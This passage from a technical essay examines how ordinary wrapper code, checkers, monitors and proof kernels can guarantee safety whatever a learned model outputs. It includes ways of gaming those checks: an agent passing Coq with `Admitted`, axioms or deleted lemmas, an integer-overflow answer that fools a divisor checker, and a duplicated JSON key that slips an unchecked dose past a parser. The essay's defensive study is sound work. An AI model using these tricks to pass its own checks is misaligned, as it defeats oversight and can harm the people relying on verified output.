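`choose_unchecked` is unsound. Each entry in the table is a function's address, which takes eight bytes on a 64-bit computer, so the five entries take 40 bytes. If the network returns 200, the program reads the eight bytes starting 1,600 bytes after the beginning of the table and treats them as a function's address, and the cart runs whatever is there. According to Rust's documentation for `get_unchecked`, using an index outside the table is undefined behaviour even if the program never uses the result, so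 checking the number after fetching the entry would be too late.

`choose_or_stop` fixes the fault with a range check and a default. If the number is between 0 and 4, `i` is that number, and otherwise `i` is 0. Either way `i` is less than 5, which meets the contract of `get_unchecked`. These two cases are the whole proof, however many weights the network has and even if someone trained it to crash the program.

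An enum, a type with a fixed list of values, requires the same care as a table of functions. Reinterpreting the byte 200 as a value of a five-value enum is immediately undefined behaviour, because Rust requires every enum value to be one of those listed. A `match` that maps the five valid numbers to their enum values and every other number to `stop` avoids the problem without unsafe code.

All this assumes that `net.run` is sound. Many programs run their networks through large C or C++ libraries, and a memory error there would undermine the Rust code as well. The error would be in the library's code, so isolating the library, as Omniglot does, addresses it without anyone having to understand the weights.

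So a Rust library can meet Rust's own soundness criterion with any learned model inside it, just as `BTreeMap` can with any ordering.

### A valid action can be the wrong one

If the network returns 1, the cart goes forward, even if somebody is standing in front of it. Rust's reference does not classify incorrect results as unsafe, so a wrong output that makes the cart hit a person is not unsafe in Rust's sense.

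Rust's soundness criterion doesn't justify the choice of default either. Changing the 0 in `choose_or_stop` to a 1 would make the cart drive forward whenever the network returned nonsense, and the function would still be sound. Whether stopping is a sensible default depends on the warehouse, though in most it is.

The people who run the warehouse want a guarantee about the cart, for example that it never receives a command to exceed walking pace. This guarantee can follow Rust's criterion, with the event they want to rule out in place of undefined behaviour.

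### The restated criterion

Let *W* be the wrapper, the ordinary code through which all use of the model passes. Let *E* be the forbidden event, so that *E*(*r*) means that the event happens in run *r*. Let *B* be the model's behaviour, which gives its output for each input, possibly depending on everything that came before. *W* excludes *E* if and only if

∀*C* ∈ Clients(*W*), ∀*B* ∈ Behaviours, ∀*r* ∈ Runs(*C* + *W* + *B*): ¬*E*(*r*)

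The behaviours include every output the model's output type allows, in every order, and no output at all. They therefore cover every set of weights, every training method, and models that choose their outputs at random. The formula does not account for how likely a behaviour is, so it treats a model that fails once in a billion runs the same as one that fails every time.

Computer security researchers have used similar definitions for years. *Journey Beyond Full Abstraction* (Abate, Blanco and colleagues, 2018) says that a piece of a program robustly satisfies a property if it satisfies the property whatever code it is linked with, including hostile code. Here the piece is the wrapper, and the other code is the client and the model together.

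*Robust Safety for Move* (2021) applies the idea to Move, a language for programs that manage digital assets on a blockchain. Its forbidden event is a violation of an invariant the programmer has written down. No attacker can violate the invariant if the Move code is well typed, its author has proved that it maintains the invariant, and outside code can't reach the data involved. *Cerisier* (2026) concerns processors on which a program can use memory only if it holds a capability for that memory. It builds on a "universal contract", a guarantee that arbitrary code never exceeds the authority of the capabilities it can get.

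Both results hold for any code, so they apply to neural networks even though neither is about them. More recently, researchers have stated guarantees of this type for language models, and *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) explicitly calls for guarantees that don't depend on the model's behaviour.

A safe Rust client cannot cause undefined behaviour on its own, but it can make a cart go too fast if it has access to the motor. The restated criterion can therefore hold only for clients that cannot cause the event without the wrapper, and Rust's compiler does not automatically enforce this restriction.

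### Defining the event

Suppose that a newer network returns a speed in metres per second, and that the forbidden event is "the wrapper sends the motor a speed greater than 2". A programmer might write this:

```rust
let safe = if speed > 2.0 { 2.0 } else { speed };
```

The wrapper now meets the criterion, but the cart is still not safe. The network could return −50, which is not greater than 2 and may mean reversing at 50 metres per second. It could also return NaN ("not a number"), the result of calculations such as zero divided by zero. Every greater-than comparison with NaN is false, so NaN reaches the motor. The motor's response then depends on how its manufacturer handled NaN, which may never have come up in testing.

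The code does what the definition asked for, so the definition has to change. A better one is "the wrapper sends the motor anything other than a number from 0 to 2":

```rust
let safe = if (0.0..=2.0).contains(&speed) { speed } else { 0.0 };
```

This version replaces −50, NaN and every other unacceptable value with 0. The criterion covers every behaviour, so the model may do anything the definition does not rule out, including output NaN, which one might never consider with a human driver or a conventional program.

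Even the better definition covers only the command sent to the cart. A loaded cart on a steep ramp may still roll faster than 2 metres per second after the wrapper sends a stop command. Engineers would have to deal with that through brakes and tests, and the proof about the wrapper gives them one fact to start from.

The speed limit has a one-line definition that is final, whereas soundness depends on Rust's list of undefined behaviours, which is incomplete and may change.

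### Recognising the event in time

A wrapper can refuse an output only on the basis of what has happened so far. In *Enforceable Security Policies*, Schneider (2000) proved that, because of this limit, monitors can enforce only safety properties. A monitor is a component that watches a program's steps and stops it before a step that would break a rule. A safety property is a rule for which every violation happens at a definite point and cannot be put right by anything that follows.

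One of his examples is a rule that a program must not send messages after it has read a file. The monitor needs only two states, "no file read yet" and "file read", and switches to the second when the program reads a file. If the program then tries to send a message, the monitor stops it. The rule works for any program because enforcing it doesn't depend on why the program is sending the message.

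A monitor can never detect that a program has broken a rule that nobody has to wait forever for a resource, because however long somebody has waited, the resource might still become available. Adding a time limit turns the rule into a safety property, because the violation then happens when the time runs out.

But a monitor may detect that moment without being able to prevent it. In *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, Basin, Jugé and colleagues (2012) distinguish actions that a monitor can control from those it can only observe, such as the ticking of a clock. A monitor can enforce a rule that nobody may log in for three time units after a failure, because it can refuse logins. It can't enforce a rule that every request must lead to a delivery within three time units, because it can't stop the clock, and stopping the program doesn't produce a delivery.

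Similarly, the cart's wrapper can keep the cart still for three seconds after a bump, but it can't make a slow network respond within a tenth of a second. The wrapper can send its own command when the time is up, so it is more powerful than the monitors Basin and colleagues analysed.

The monitor's check must also always finish with an answer. This matters when a model's output is itself a program, because no check can decide for every possible program whether it will ever delete a file. A wrapper that needed the answer in advance would have to reject some harmless programs. A wrapper could instead run the program and refuse any attempt to delete a file, so it can sometimes prevent an event it cannot predict.

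A wrapper that refuses everything satisfies the restated criterion, since a cart that never moves never breaks the speed limit. Schneider notes that making a monitor stricter can never cause it to violate a rule of this kind, even if it ends up allowing nothing. Basin and colleagues therefore add a second requirement, transparency: the monitor must not stop a program that is obeying the rule. Both requirements are easy to meet for the speed limit. For harder events, a wrapper's author usually has to give up some transparency to keep the guarantee, and the criterion sets no limit on how much.

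### Every route to the event

The wrapper can't enforce the speed limit if a client can call `motor.set_speed(50.0)` directly. Safe Rust allows that call if the motor's interface is public, so the wrapper has to own the motor and keep it in a private field, as a vector does with its length. Then only code in the wrapper's module can call the motor's methods, and a reviewer needs to read only that module.

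In computer security, a component with this kind of control is called a reference monitor. According to the lecture slides *Science of Security Historical Perspective*, it gets control at every event that matters to the policy, blocks events that would violate the policy, and is protected from tampering.

*Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) presents a safety theorem for language-model agents. A solver, a program that checks whether a set of logical conditions can all be true together, examines each action the model proposes. The initial state obeys the safety rules, and each action the solver allows leads to another state that obeys them, so by induction every state does, even if the model is hostile. The theorem assumes that no action can bypass the solver and that the model can neither read nor alter it.

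In the published proof, the solver looks for at least one outcome that fits the current state, the proposed action and the rules. This is enough if the state and action determine the outcome. If they allow more than one, some outcomes could obey the rules while others break them, so the solver would have to confirm that every possible outcome is safe.

Routes around a wrapper are easy to overlook, even for memory safety. On Linux, a program can open a special file that represents its own memory. Rust treats writing to a file as safe, so safe code can use this file to change memory that the compiler was protecting. Hassnain and Stanford (2024) collected this and other examples in *Counterexamples in Safe Rust*, including a program that starts a debugger and has it modify the program's memory. According to Rust's documentation, such routes are outside entities that Rust's guarantees don't cover,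 and closing them requires a sandbox, which limits what a program can reach in the operating system.

That is a reasonable position for a programming language, because hardly anyone overwrites their own program's memory by accident. But the restated criterion includes behaviours that nobody would produce by accident, so if a model can choose which files to open, the wrapper's author must count that special file among the routes.

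Other code in the same program can also break the guarantee. Abate and colleagues give the example of a cryptographic library that has been proven never to reveal its secret key. Linking that library into a browser with millions of lines of C and C++ can void the guarantee, because one memory error in the browser may let an attacker read the key directly.

Using *B* in the restated criterion also assumes that the model can only return outputs. This is true of a network that multiplies numbers and returns the result to the wrapper, but not of an agent with its own internet connection.

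### Sound libraries that break other guarantees

*We Need to Talk About the Actual Guarantees of Rust-based Systems* (Tiffany, Agvanian and colleagues, 2026) shows that sound Rust code is allowed to get around private fields. This makes them a weaker foundation for a wrapper than they seem, and several research systems rely on them.

In safe code, the compiler does more than prevent undefined behaviour. For example, it keeps private fields private and usually stops code from changing data through a shared reference. Tiffany and colleagues call these incidental properties. A library with unsafe code can break these properties and still be sound, provided no undefined behaviour results.

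Sesame, which some of the same researchers built, enforces privacy rules in web applications. It stores each sensitive value in a container with its policy, and the application can reach the value only through Sesame's functions, which check the policy first. Dak Albab, Agvanian and colleagues (*Sesame*, 2024) tried it on four web applications and reported that its automated guarantees covered 95% of the code and the rest needed manual review.

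One of the applications lets students submit homework, and a policy forbids it from logging their answers. Tiffany and colleagues wrote a small library for the common task of converting data to text. The library uses unsafe code to read the private fields of types defined in other people's libraries. When the application used it to log a submission, the student's answer appeared in the log. The application itself contained no unsafe code, and Miri found no undefined behaviour.

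Sesame can protect against this leak by storing a scrambled address in place of the data, so that only the scrambled address reaches the log. This made operations take about twice as long in small benchmarks, and it doesn't protect against code that replaces a value's policy with a more permissive one.

RedLeaf (Narayanan, Huang and colleagues, 2020) is an operating system whose parts share one region of memory. It relies on Rust's type and memory safety, rather than the usual hardware protection, to keep those parts separate. If one part crashes, the system cleans up the data that part owned and carries on. The other parts' data should be intact, because the crashed part had only shared references to it.

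Rust's standard library type `RefCell` is sound and very common. It allows changes through a shared reference and checks while the program is running that no two uses conflict. Tiffany and colleagues wrote a scheduler, the part of an operating system that decides which thread runs next, and kept its list of waiting threads in a `RefCell` shared with the kernel. If the scheduler crashes just after taking a thread off the list, RedLeaf does not put the thread back, so it never runs again.

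They confirmed similar failures in five other systems. These demonstrations used code written for the purpose and don't show that anyone's data leaked in practice. But the code is the sort that programmers write every day, and it broke no rule of Rust.

Banning all unsafe code would prevent these failures, but more than half of the 500 most used Rust libraries call unsafe code, even without counting the standard library. Several of the systems ban it only in the application, so unsafe code in the application's libraries can still break the guarantee.

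Soundness works across thousands of libraries because their authors all agreed to the same definition. Someone who wrote a text-conversion library has agreed not to cause undefined behaviour, but has never heard of the homework policy. Anyone who replaces undefined behaviour with another forbidden event can no longer rely on this agreement and has to check other people's code for the new event.

Tiffany and colleagues built a tool called Sniffer to make that manageable. A developer names the incidental property and the types it has to protect. Sniffer follows every function the program might call, including functions in other libraries, and reports operations that could violate the property. The homework application and its libraries contain 33,735 regions of unsafe code, and the part that handles submissions can reach 9,982 of them. Sniffer reported twelve operations. One was the leak, and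 eleven were false alarms that a person could dismiss by looking at how the program used them.

Twelve is few enough for a careful developer to review. Sniffer also found the RedLeaf fault, though only in excerpts, because RedLeaf doesn't work with the compiler versions that Sniffer supports. Sniffer relies on a list of the unsafe operations that can break each property, and it would not report an operation missing from that list. It also relies on a person who wants to get the right answer. Tiffany and colleagues say that if the code's author may be hostile, the system needs nearly perfect tools, because it cannot leave doubtful cases to the author's judgement.

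### Combining guarantees

A program may need several guarantees at once. Schneider shows that this is simple for monitors that can only stop a program. If one monitor enforces a speed limit and another keeps the cart out of the loading bay, running both enforces both rules, since each can only remove runs from those the other allows.

Wrappers that substitute their own actions need more care. Suppose one wrapper stops the cart whenever the network's output is invalid, and another forbids stopping in front of the fire door. Either works alone, but they conflict if the output is invalid while the cart is in front of the fire door. Their designers have to find an action that satisfies both rules, or make sure the cart never gets into that position. Rust's developers faced a similar problem in 2015, when `Rc` and scoped threads turned out to rely on incompatible assumptions.

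Confidentiality doesn't combine so easily either, because it is not a safety property. Suppose a model knows a building's four-digit door code, and a wrapper blocks any reply that contains it. A visitor who asks the model to repeat each number from 0000 to 9999 receives 9,999 replies, and the missing number is the code. The wrapper met its guarantee, since the code never appeared in a reply. No single run shows the leak, because the leak is a difference between what happens with one code and what would have happened with another.

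Schneider concludes that no monitor can enforce exactly the absence of information flow. Removing runs never violates a safety property, but it can create a leak. A monitor can only enforce a stricter rule, such as one that the model never receives the code.

Abate and colleagues arrange properties by how hard they are to guarantee against hostile code. Confining that code and preventing it from changing the program's data is enough for safety properties. Confidentiality also requires hiding the data from the hostile code, which may need quite different protection.

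A proof that covers all runs together can establish confidentiality, although a monitor that watches one run cannot. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) presents a small language for writing agents that call language models, and a computer-checked theorem that applies to every program in it, including agents that write and run their own code. The theorem is a form of noninterference, which roughly means that changing the secret doesn't change the probabilities of what an outsider sees. Like most guarantees of this kind, it ignores what an outsider could learn from whether the program finishes.

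### Specifying the event and not the model

The proofs for the action table and the speed limit don't refer to the model's weights, its training data, or any account of what a good answer would be, so they still hold after the model is retrained. The restated criterion covers every behaviour the model could have, so it doesn't require a full specification of the model's behaviour, which nobody has. It does require a specification of the event, which can be very short.

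For some events this makes no difference, because defining the event requires specifying the model. Suppose a post office uses the digit-reading network from earlier to sort letters. "The machine sends a letter to a bin that doesn't exist" is a precise event, and a range check excludes it. "The network misreads a digit" isn't precise, because nobody has a definition of which images show which digits.

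Other events have a clear definition but depend on information the wrapper doesn't have. Suppose a model that answers questions about medicines tells someone with a headache, "You can take two more tablets now." This is fine if the person last took some yesterday, but it could seriously harm someone who has already taken the maximum dose today and didn't mention it. A court could decide afterwards whether the person came to harm by following the advice, but the wrapper can't distinguish the two cases because the conversation is the same in both.

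No improvement in the wrapper's code can solve this. Write obs(*r*) for everything that the wrapper has seen in run *r* when it has to decide whether to release the reply. Suppose that there are two runs in which releasing the reply would lead to different results:

obs(*r*₁) = obs(*r*₂), with harm in *r*₁ and none in *r*₂

The wrapper's decision can depend only on the information it receives, which is the same in both runs, so it must make the same decision in both. Choosing at random doesn't help, because it would sometimes release the harmful reply. Releasing the reply allows the forbidden event in *r*₁, while refusing withholds good advice in *r*₂. When almost any reply could harm some possible reader, a wrapper that guarantees no harm has to refuse almost everything.

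The wrapper could gather more information by asking how many tablets the person has taken today, which would distinguish the two runs if the person answers correctly. But people forget and sometimes lie, and the wrapper can't control what they do once the reply is on the screen. In Basin and colleagues' terms, the person's next action is at best observable, and usually the wrapper can't observe it.

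The harm may also be hard to recognise even when the text contains all the relevant information. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) proves under standard cryptographic assumptions that efficient filters for harmful text cannot work for every model.

The cart raises a milder version of the same problem. Whether it hits somebody depends on where people are, and the wrapper gets this information only from sensors. The wrapper can guarantee that the cart never gets an order to move forward while the distance sensor reads less than a metre. Whether that prevents collisions depends on the sensor, the brakes and how suddenly people step out, but engineers can measure all of these.

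The medicine wrapper's developer can similarly make a narrower promise, for instance that no reply gives a dose larger than the one printed in an approved table. A program can check this if replies give doses in a fixed format. The guarantee would then hold for every model and every reader, even a reader who has already taken the maximum dose and would be harmed by two more tablets. Somebody would have to follow up with readers to find out how often such harm occurs.

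## Checking what the model produces

The medicine wrapper lets the model write any reply, but ordinary code compares the doses with the approved table and releases only the replies that pass. The wrapper's author could instead have the code offer the model only correct options to choose from.

### Choosing among correct options

Compilers often replace a call to a function with a copy of the function's body, which programmers call inlining:

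```rust
fn square(x: i32) -> i32 { x * x }
fn before(n: i32) -> i32 { square(n) + 1 }
fn after(n: i32) -> i32 { n * n + 1 }
```

Inlining `square` turns `before` into `after`, which returns the same result for every `n`. Inlining removes the overhead of a call and often makes further optimizations possible, but it also makes the program bigger, which can slow it down because less of it fits in the processor's cache. Nobody has a simple rule for which calls are worth inlining, so the decision suits a learned model.

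Suppose a program has 50 calls that the compiler knows how to inline correctly. A learned policy answers yes or no for each, which gives 2⁵⁰ possible programs, all with the same results. The compiler does the rewriting, so the policy never touches the code. If *O*(*s*) is the set of options that the wrapper offers in situation *s*, the wrapper's author has to establish that

∀*s*, ∀*o* ∈ *O*(*s*): Correct(*s*, *o*)

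If the policy returns something that isn't on the list, the wrapper leaves the call unchanged. A terrible policy can make the program slow or bloated, but not incorrect.

This depends on the compiler's inlining code being correct for every option, including those a hand-written rule would never pick. It also depends on what "correct" covers. Rust doesn't guarantee how long a calculation takes, so a different inlining choice could change the timing of a cryptographic function and help an attacker who measures it. If the program has undefined behaviour, the 2⁵⁰ versions may behave differently from one another.

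Researchers use the same arrangement to analyse programs. *Agentic Interpretation* (Mitchell and Wang, 2026) cites systems in which a language model guides an analyser, but only through decisions that can't affect the analyser's soundness.

### Testing each answer

Often nobody can list the correct options in advance, but a program can recognise one. Take the greatest common divisor of two positive numbers *a* and *b*, the largest number that divides both. The model returns its answer *g* and two more whole numbers, *u* and *v*, as evidence:

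```rust
pub struct Gcd { a: i64, b: i64, g: i64 }

impl Gcd {
    pub fn check(a: i64, b: i64, g: i64, u: i64, v: i64) -> Option<Gcd> {
        let ok = a > 0 && b > 0 && g > 0
            && a % g == 0
            && b % g == 0
            && u * a + v * b == g;
        if ok { Some(Gcd { a, b, g }) } else { None }
    }
}
```

For 84 and 30, the model might return 6, with −1 and 3 as evidence. Six divides both numbers, and −1 × 84 + 3 × 30 = 6. The last equation shows that no larger number will do, because anything that divides both *a* and *b* also divides *ua* + *vb*, which is *g*. If the model answers 3 instead, it can't find suitable evidence, since 84*u* + 30*v* is always a multiple of 6. (All this assumes exact arithmetic.)

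The fields are private, so a client can get a `Gcd` only through `check`. Any function that takes a `Gcd` can rely on the answer, and the compiler rejects a program that passes it an unchecked answer.

For an input *x*, an output *y*, evidence *w* and a statement *S*, a checker should satisfy

∀*x*, ∀*y*, ∀*w*: Accept(*x*, *y*, *w*) ⇒ *S*(*x*, *y*)

The model doesn't appear in the formula, so a wrapper that releases only accepted outputs never releases a *y* for which *S* is false, whatever the model does.

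### Program checkers

The University of Washington's *CSE 531* presents checking a program's answers one at a time as a weaker alternative to verifying the whole program. Mori and Itoh's *On Checkers, Self-Testers, and Self-Debuggers* credits this idea to Manuel Blum and Sampath Kannan, who describe it in *Designing Programs that Check Their Work* (1995).

*Fast Checkers for Cryptography* (Kompella and Adleman, 1991) gives Blum's definition of a program checker. The checker takes a program *P* that finishes on every input, a particular input *I*, and a confidence level *k*, and it may also run *P* on other inputs.

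- If *P* is right on every input, the checker answers CORRECT with probability at least 1 − 2⁻ᵏ.
- If *P* is wrong on *I*, the checker answers BUGGY with probability at least 1 − 2⁻ᵏ.

With *k* = 20, the checker approves a wrong answer less than one time in a million. If *P* is right on *I* but wrong on some other input, the definition permits either verdict from the checker.

Kompella and Adleman built a checker for a calculation used in RSA encryption, which raises *a* to the power *b* and keeps the remainder after dividing by *m*. It relies on the rule that *a*ᵇ × *a*ᶠ = *a*ᵇ⁺ᶠ. Suppose *P* computes the remainder of 3⁵ divided by 7 and returns 4 instead of 5. The checker picks another exponent at random, say 2, and has *P* compute the remainders for 3² and 3⁷. *P* correctly returns 2 and 3. But 4 × 2 is 8, which has a remainder of 1 when divided by 7, not 3, so the checker reports a bug.

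A program that always returns 1 would pass this test, because 1 × 1 = 1. The checker must therefore first establish that *P* is right for most exponents. It starts with squaring, which it can verify directly, and works up to exponents with twice as many digits each time, using *P* for most of the calculation.

A useful checker must be much faster than solving the problem. Otherwise its author could run a correct program and compare the answers. For an exponent with 2,048 binary digits, the usual method needs at least about 2,000 multiplications. The checker needs about 11 stages, though each stage involves many repetitions.

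Blum's definition treats *P* as a fixed function, which suits a digit-reading network. A chatbot that remembers earlier questions isn't a fixed function, so its later answers can be consistent with an earlier mistake. In the example, it could answer 4 for 3⁵ and then 1 for 3⁷, and pass the test.

### Self-proving models

Amit, Goldwasser and colleagues (2024), in *Models That Prove Their Own Correctness*, define a guarantee that also covers models that adapt their answers. They train a model to answer a question and then convince a verifier, over one or more rounds of questions, that the answer is right. People write the verifier by hand and prove that it is sound, meaning that for every input *x*, every wrong answer *y* and every prover *P*,

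Pr[the verifier accepts *y* after questioning *P*] ≤ *s*

Here *s* is a small error, and the probability comes from random choices during the conversation. The prover may have unlimited computing power and know exactly how the verifier works.

The guarantee about the model's own success is weaker because it holds only on average over a chosen distribution of inputs. Amit and colleagues call a model β-self-proving if the verifier accepts its answers with probability at least β over that distribution. If the verifier accepts a wrong answer with probability at most *s* on any input, such a model is right at least β − *s* of the time on the distribution. With β = 0.95 and *s* = 0.01, that is 94%. On other kinds of input the model might never convince the verifier, but the verifier still accepts wrong answers at most 1% of the time.

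| Guarantee | Inputs covered | Programs or models covered |
|---|---|---|
| A program checker flags a wrong answer | every input | every fixed program that always finishes |
| A program checker approves a right answer | every input | only programs that are right on every input |
| A sound verifier refuses a wrong answer | every input | every prover |
| A self-proving model gets its answers accepted | the average over one distribution | one trained model |

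The 1% limits how often the verifier accepts a wrong answer. The share of accepted answers that are wrong can be higher, and it is 100% if the model is always wrong. Retrying increases the chance of releasing a wrong answer. If a wrapper asks a model that is always wrong up to 100 times and stops at the first acceptance, that chance could reach 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or 63%. The wrapper can reduce it by repeating the verification of each answer with fresh random choices. Five independent repetitions reduce *s* from one in a hundred to one in ten billion.

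Amit and colleagues also trained a small network to compute greatest common divisors and prove its answers. One of their training methods rewards the model whenever the verifier accepts. Better training raises β but doesn't change *s*, which depends only on the verifier.

### Proof kernels and Aria

*What mathematicians should know about the Lean Theorem Prover* (Hales, 2026) describes a formal proof as one checked exhaustively down to the foundations of mathematics and the basic rules of logic. Coq and Lean each have a proof kernel that does this checking mechanically. The kernel's check has no random error, so a million failed attempts don't make the next acceptance less reliable.

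In *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification*, Kan, Kan and Ertel (2026) tested an agent called Aria on RustBelt, the Coq proof that Rust's type system and several of its libraries are safe. They deleted the proofs of 217 lemmas about `Arc`, `Mutex`, `Vec` and five other library types, left the statements in place, and had Aria write new proofs. Aria uses Claude Opus 4.7 as a general coding agent. It had no internet access and couldn't see the project's history, so it couldn't look up the originals. Coq checked each attempt. If a step failed, Aria received the line number, the error message and whatever still needed proving at that point. It could retry up to 30 times.

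Aria proved all 217 lemmas, 73% on the first attempt and 86% within one retry. The hardest, such as those about copying and destroying an `Arc`, needed up to 13 retries. Each lemma took an average of about 12 minutes of model time.

The first attempt failed for about 59 lemmas. If Aria had given up on them, RustBelt would have been missing those proofs but would have contained no false ones. A weaker model leaves more proofs missing but does not increase the risk of a false one. On 40 short lemmas from another project, the open-source model Kimi K2.6 also proved everything but took about seven times as long as Opus. It often failed on proofs longer than about fifty lines.

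RustBelt's proofs have been public for years, so the model may have seen them in training. That would make the result less impressive, but it wouldn't affect whether the proofs are correct. Aria also proved 72 lemmas that nobody had yet proved in Lean, although Coq versions existed. In all these tests, people had already written the statements and definitions, which is a large part of the work in a project like RustBelt.

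An agent that can edit the file has easier ways to pass the kernel's check than finding a proof. It can delete the lemma, weaken it, declare it an axiom, or end the proof with `Admitted`, which makes Coq accept the lemma unproved. Kan and colleagues therefore surround the agent with ordinary code that blocks such edits and confirms that every original lemma is present and unchanged. The person who wants the proof must choose *S*, and the model must be unable to change it.

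### Certificates for language-model pipelines

Most language model output is not a formal proof, but parts of it may still have precise properties. *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines* (Koomullil, 2026) proposes attaching a Lean-checked certificate to each of these parts.

In one of Koomullil's examples, a system that advises doctors splits a recommendation into separate claims and reports 95% support for them. But one claim, that the patient's kidneys work well enough for the drug, contradicts the drug's official label, which the system retrieved. A score that measures only support doesn't reflect this contradiction, so Koomullil's certificate also adds up the weight of the contradicted claims and blocks the recommendation if the total exceeds a limit.

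Lean can check that the total is right and that the rule blocks what it should, which Koomullil calls computational verification. But other models divide the text into claims and decide which passages contradict them, and Lean does not check their decisions. The certificates do not provide semantic verification, which would show that the medical advice is correct.

In a test on a public set of questions, the certificate caught every contradiction Koomullil had planted and wrongly blocked 6.4% of the other answers. A simpler method based on text similarity had to wrongly block 26.6% to catch them all. Koomullil had revised the hypotheses before this run, so the result is weaker evidence than a first attempt would be.

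In a second test, an agent worked with files, and Lean checked that each action met a set of conditions before it could take effect. This blocked 67% of the unsafe actions that Koomullil injected, short of the 95% target but more than the 28% blocked by a list of forbidden patterns. It blocked no harmless actions. The remaining third of the unsafe actions got through because they met all the written conditions.

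### When the checker is wrong

The `Gcd` checker is unsound, because 64-bit multiplication isn't exact. Suppose a model claims that the greatest common divisor of 3 and 3 is 1, and offers *v* = 0 and

*u* = −6,148,914,691,236,517,205

The exact value of 3*u* is 1 − 2⁶⁴, which doesn't fit in 64 bits. If the build settings make overflow wrap around, the result is 1, and the checker accepts. Multiplying in 128 bits fixes the bug.

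An ordinary algorithm would never produce this *u*, so ordinary tests would probably miss the bug. But training that rewards a model for every accepted answer would reward this one too.

Lean's kernel had a soundness bug. In July 2026 Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture. According to *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* (de Moura, 2026), the kernel had failed to check one argument in a certain kind of definition, a gap that could be used to prove anything. Lean's developers fixed the bug an hour after Kiran Gopinathan reported it.

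Lean users can recheck a proof with nanoda, a separate kernel written in Rust. But a week-old copy of nanoda also accepted the disproof, because of an unrelated bug that its developers had recently fixed. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2* (2026) adds that the Lean bug also worked against comparator, a tool for checking proofs that may be dishonest. Less than a week earlier, The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1* (2026) announced a fix for another kernel bug, which Patrick Hulin found with GPT-5.6 Sol.

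Bugs outside the kernel also matter. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) shows Lean displaying check marks beside a few lines of nonsense. The kernel was sound, but there was a bug in a function that extracts part of a string.

Lean now comes with four additional kernels, as de Moura explains in *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (2026). Claude wrote one of them, con-leche, under close human supervision, and proved it consistent. Another, con-ron, is a Rust translation of con-leche with a proof that it follows the same checking algorithm. If a bug in Lean's compiler makes con-leche accept a false proof, the Rust compiler is unlikely to have the same bug.

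This makes a false acceptance much less likely, but we still have to trust the official kernel, which checked con-leche's consistency proof, and the proof's assumption that the set theory it uses is consistent.

### A correct proof of the wrong statement

Goldbach's conjecture says that every even number greater than 2 is the sum of two primes. Karazoupis (2026), in *The Limits of Machine-Certified Mathematics in the Age of Artificial Intelligence*, wrote a deliberately misleading version in Lean. Instead of requiring two primes *p* and *q* to add up exactly to the target *n*, it in effect requires

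*p* + *q* − *n* = 0

In ordinary arithmetic this means the same thing. But Lean's natural numbers have no negatives, so subtracting a larger number from a smaller one gives 0. The primes 3 and 3 therefore satisfy the condition for every *n* from 6 upwards. For *n* = 20, Lean calculates 6 − 20 as 0. All six kernel checks correctly accepted the proof, because it proves the statement as written. Karazoupis tested the pair 3 and 3 on 999,998 even numbers, and it was a real solution for only one of them, 6.

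A reader could spot that mistake in a single line. Such mistakes are much harder to spot when a statement depends on hundreds of definitions that an AI system also wrote. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026) discusses the 722 mathematics papers that OpenAI released in October, about 45% of which came with Lean code. According to Xena, AI-generated Lean code is informative only after some further tests, which nobody has yet run systematically on these papers.

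*Navier–Stokes Lost in Translation* (Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen, 2026) shows that no algorithm can always translate mathematical prose into Lean faithfully, because resolving the prose's ambiguities is harder than the halting problem. It also shows that the Lean proof accompanying OpenAI's result on the Navier–Stokes equations of fluid flow doesn't correspond to the written proof. The Lean code therefore doesn't verify the written argument, though it can still prove a theorem by a different route. Hales lists a Navier–Stokes result among formalised theorems.

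A kernel cannot correct a wrong statement because it has no access to what the author meant, so people have to read the statement and the definitions it uses. These are usually much shorter than the proof, which nobody needs to read.

### Refusals and delays

Aria's record was unusually good, but its slowest proof, about a kind of automaton, took 5.8 hours. One lemma in Iris, the logic underlying RustBelt, needed 28 of the 30 permitted retries. Waiting overnight for a proof is acceptable in a software project, but not when a warehouse cart needs its next command.

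The check may also never finish. Some commands in Coq proofs can search forever, so Kan and colleagues stop any command that runs for 300 seconds and treat the attempt as a failure. This time limit may reject a valid proof, but it never accepts an invalid one.

Koomullil's system can release part of an answer instead of refusing all of it. It keeps the most valuable set of claims that pass the checks and records the ones it drops. But dropping claims can change the answer's meaning. If the system keeps "this drug relieves the pain" and drops "patients with kidney disease shouldn't take it", the answer is worse than before, even though every remaining claim may be well supported.

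### Reading the output

A parser usually has to turn a model's answer from text into data before a checker can test it. In *AI Security is a LangSec Problem*, von Hippel and Miyazono warn that developers usually run these parsers inside the main application, without isolation. An attacker who can influence the model may be able to make it write text that exploits a bug in the parser before any check takes place.

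Proofs about the rest of the program don't help. kirancodes.me's *log who watches the watchers* describes tests of a verified Lean library for zip files. A 156-byte file claimed to contain 2⁶⁴ − 1 bytes of compressed data. The library's archive parser passed that size along without checking it, and Lean's own supporting code then wrote past the end of a buffer. Neither fault was in code that the proofs covered.

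A parser written entirely in safe Rust shouldn't corrupt memory, but it can still crash or use up all the memory available. It can also undermine the check without having any bug, if the program reads the text twice. Suppose a model writes

```json
{"tablets": 2, "tablets": 20}
```

If a field appears twice, some parsers keep the first value and others keep the last. If the checker's parser reads 2 and the dispensing machine's parser reads 20, the machine dispenses a dose that nobody checked. The program should parse the text once and pass on the checked value instead of the text. The `Gcd` type enforces this for its answers, because a function that requires a `Gcd` won't accept anything else.

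### Questions without a checker

Mitchell and Wang list questions that are too difficult to check formally, or whose evidence is too informal, when reasoning about programs. They include whether a library is safe if its source code isn't available and whether a newly announced vulnerability affects the version in use. The answers depend on documentation, security advisories and unwritten conventions.

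For these questions, Mitchell and Wang propose splitting the problem into small claims. A language model looks for evidence for and against each claim and grades both as absent, weak or strong. Later evidence can raise a grade but never lower it, so each claim's grades can change at most four times in total and the process must end. The recorded grades show which claims are in dispute. But nothing guarantees that the model grades the evidence correctly, and they haven't yet built or tested the system.

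A second model could also do the checking. *Human-LLM Deliberation as Interactive Proof* (2026) points out that most work on verifying models either uses verification for training or assumes that the verifier checks correctly. That assumption is hard to justify for a learned verifier, which may accept every output if nothing constrains its behaviour.

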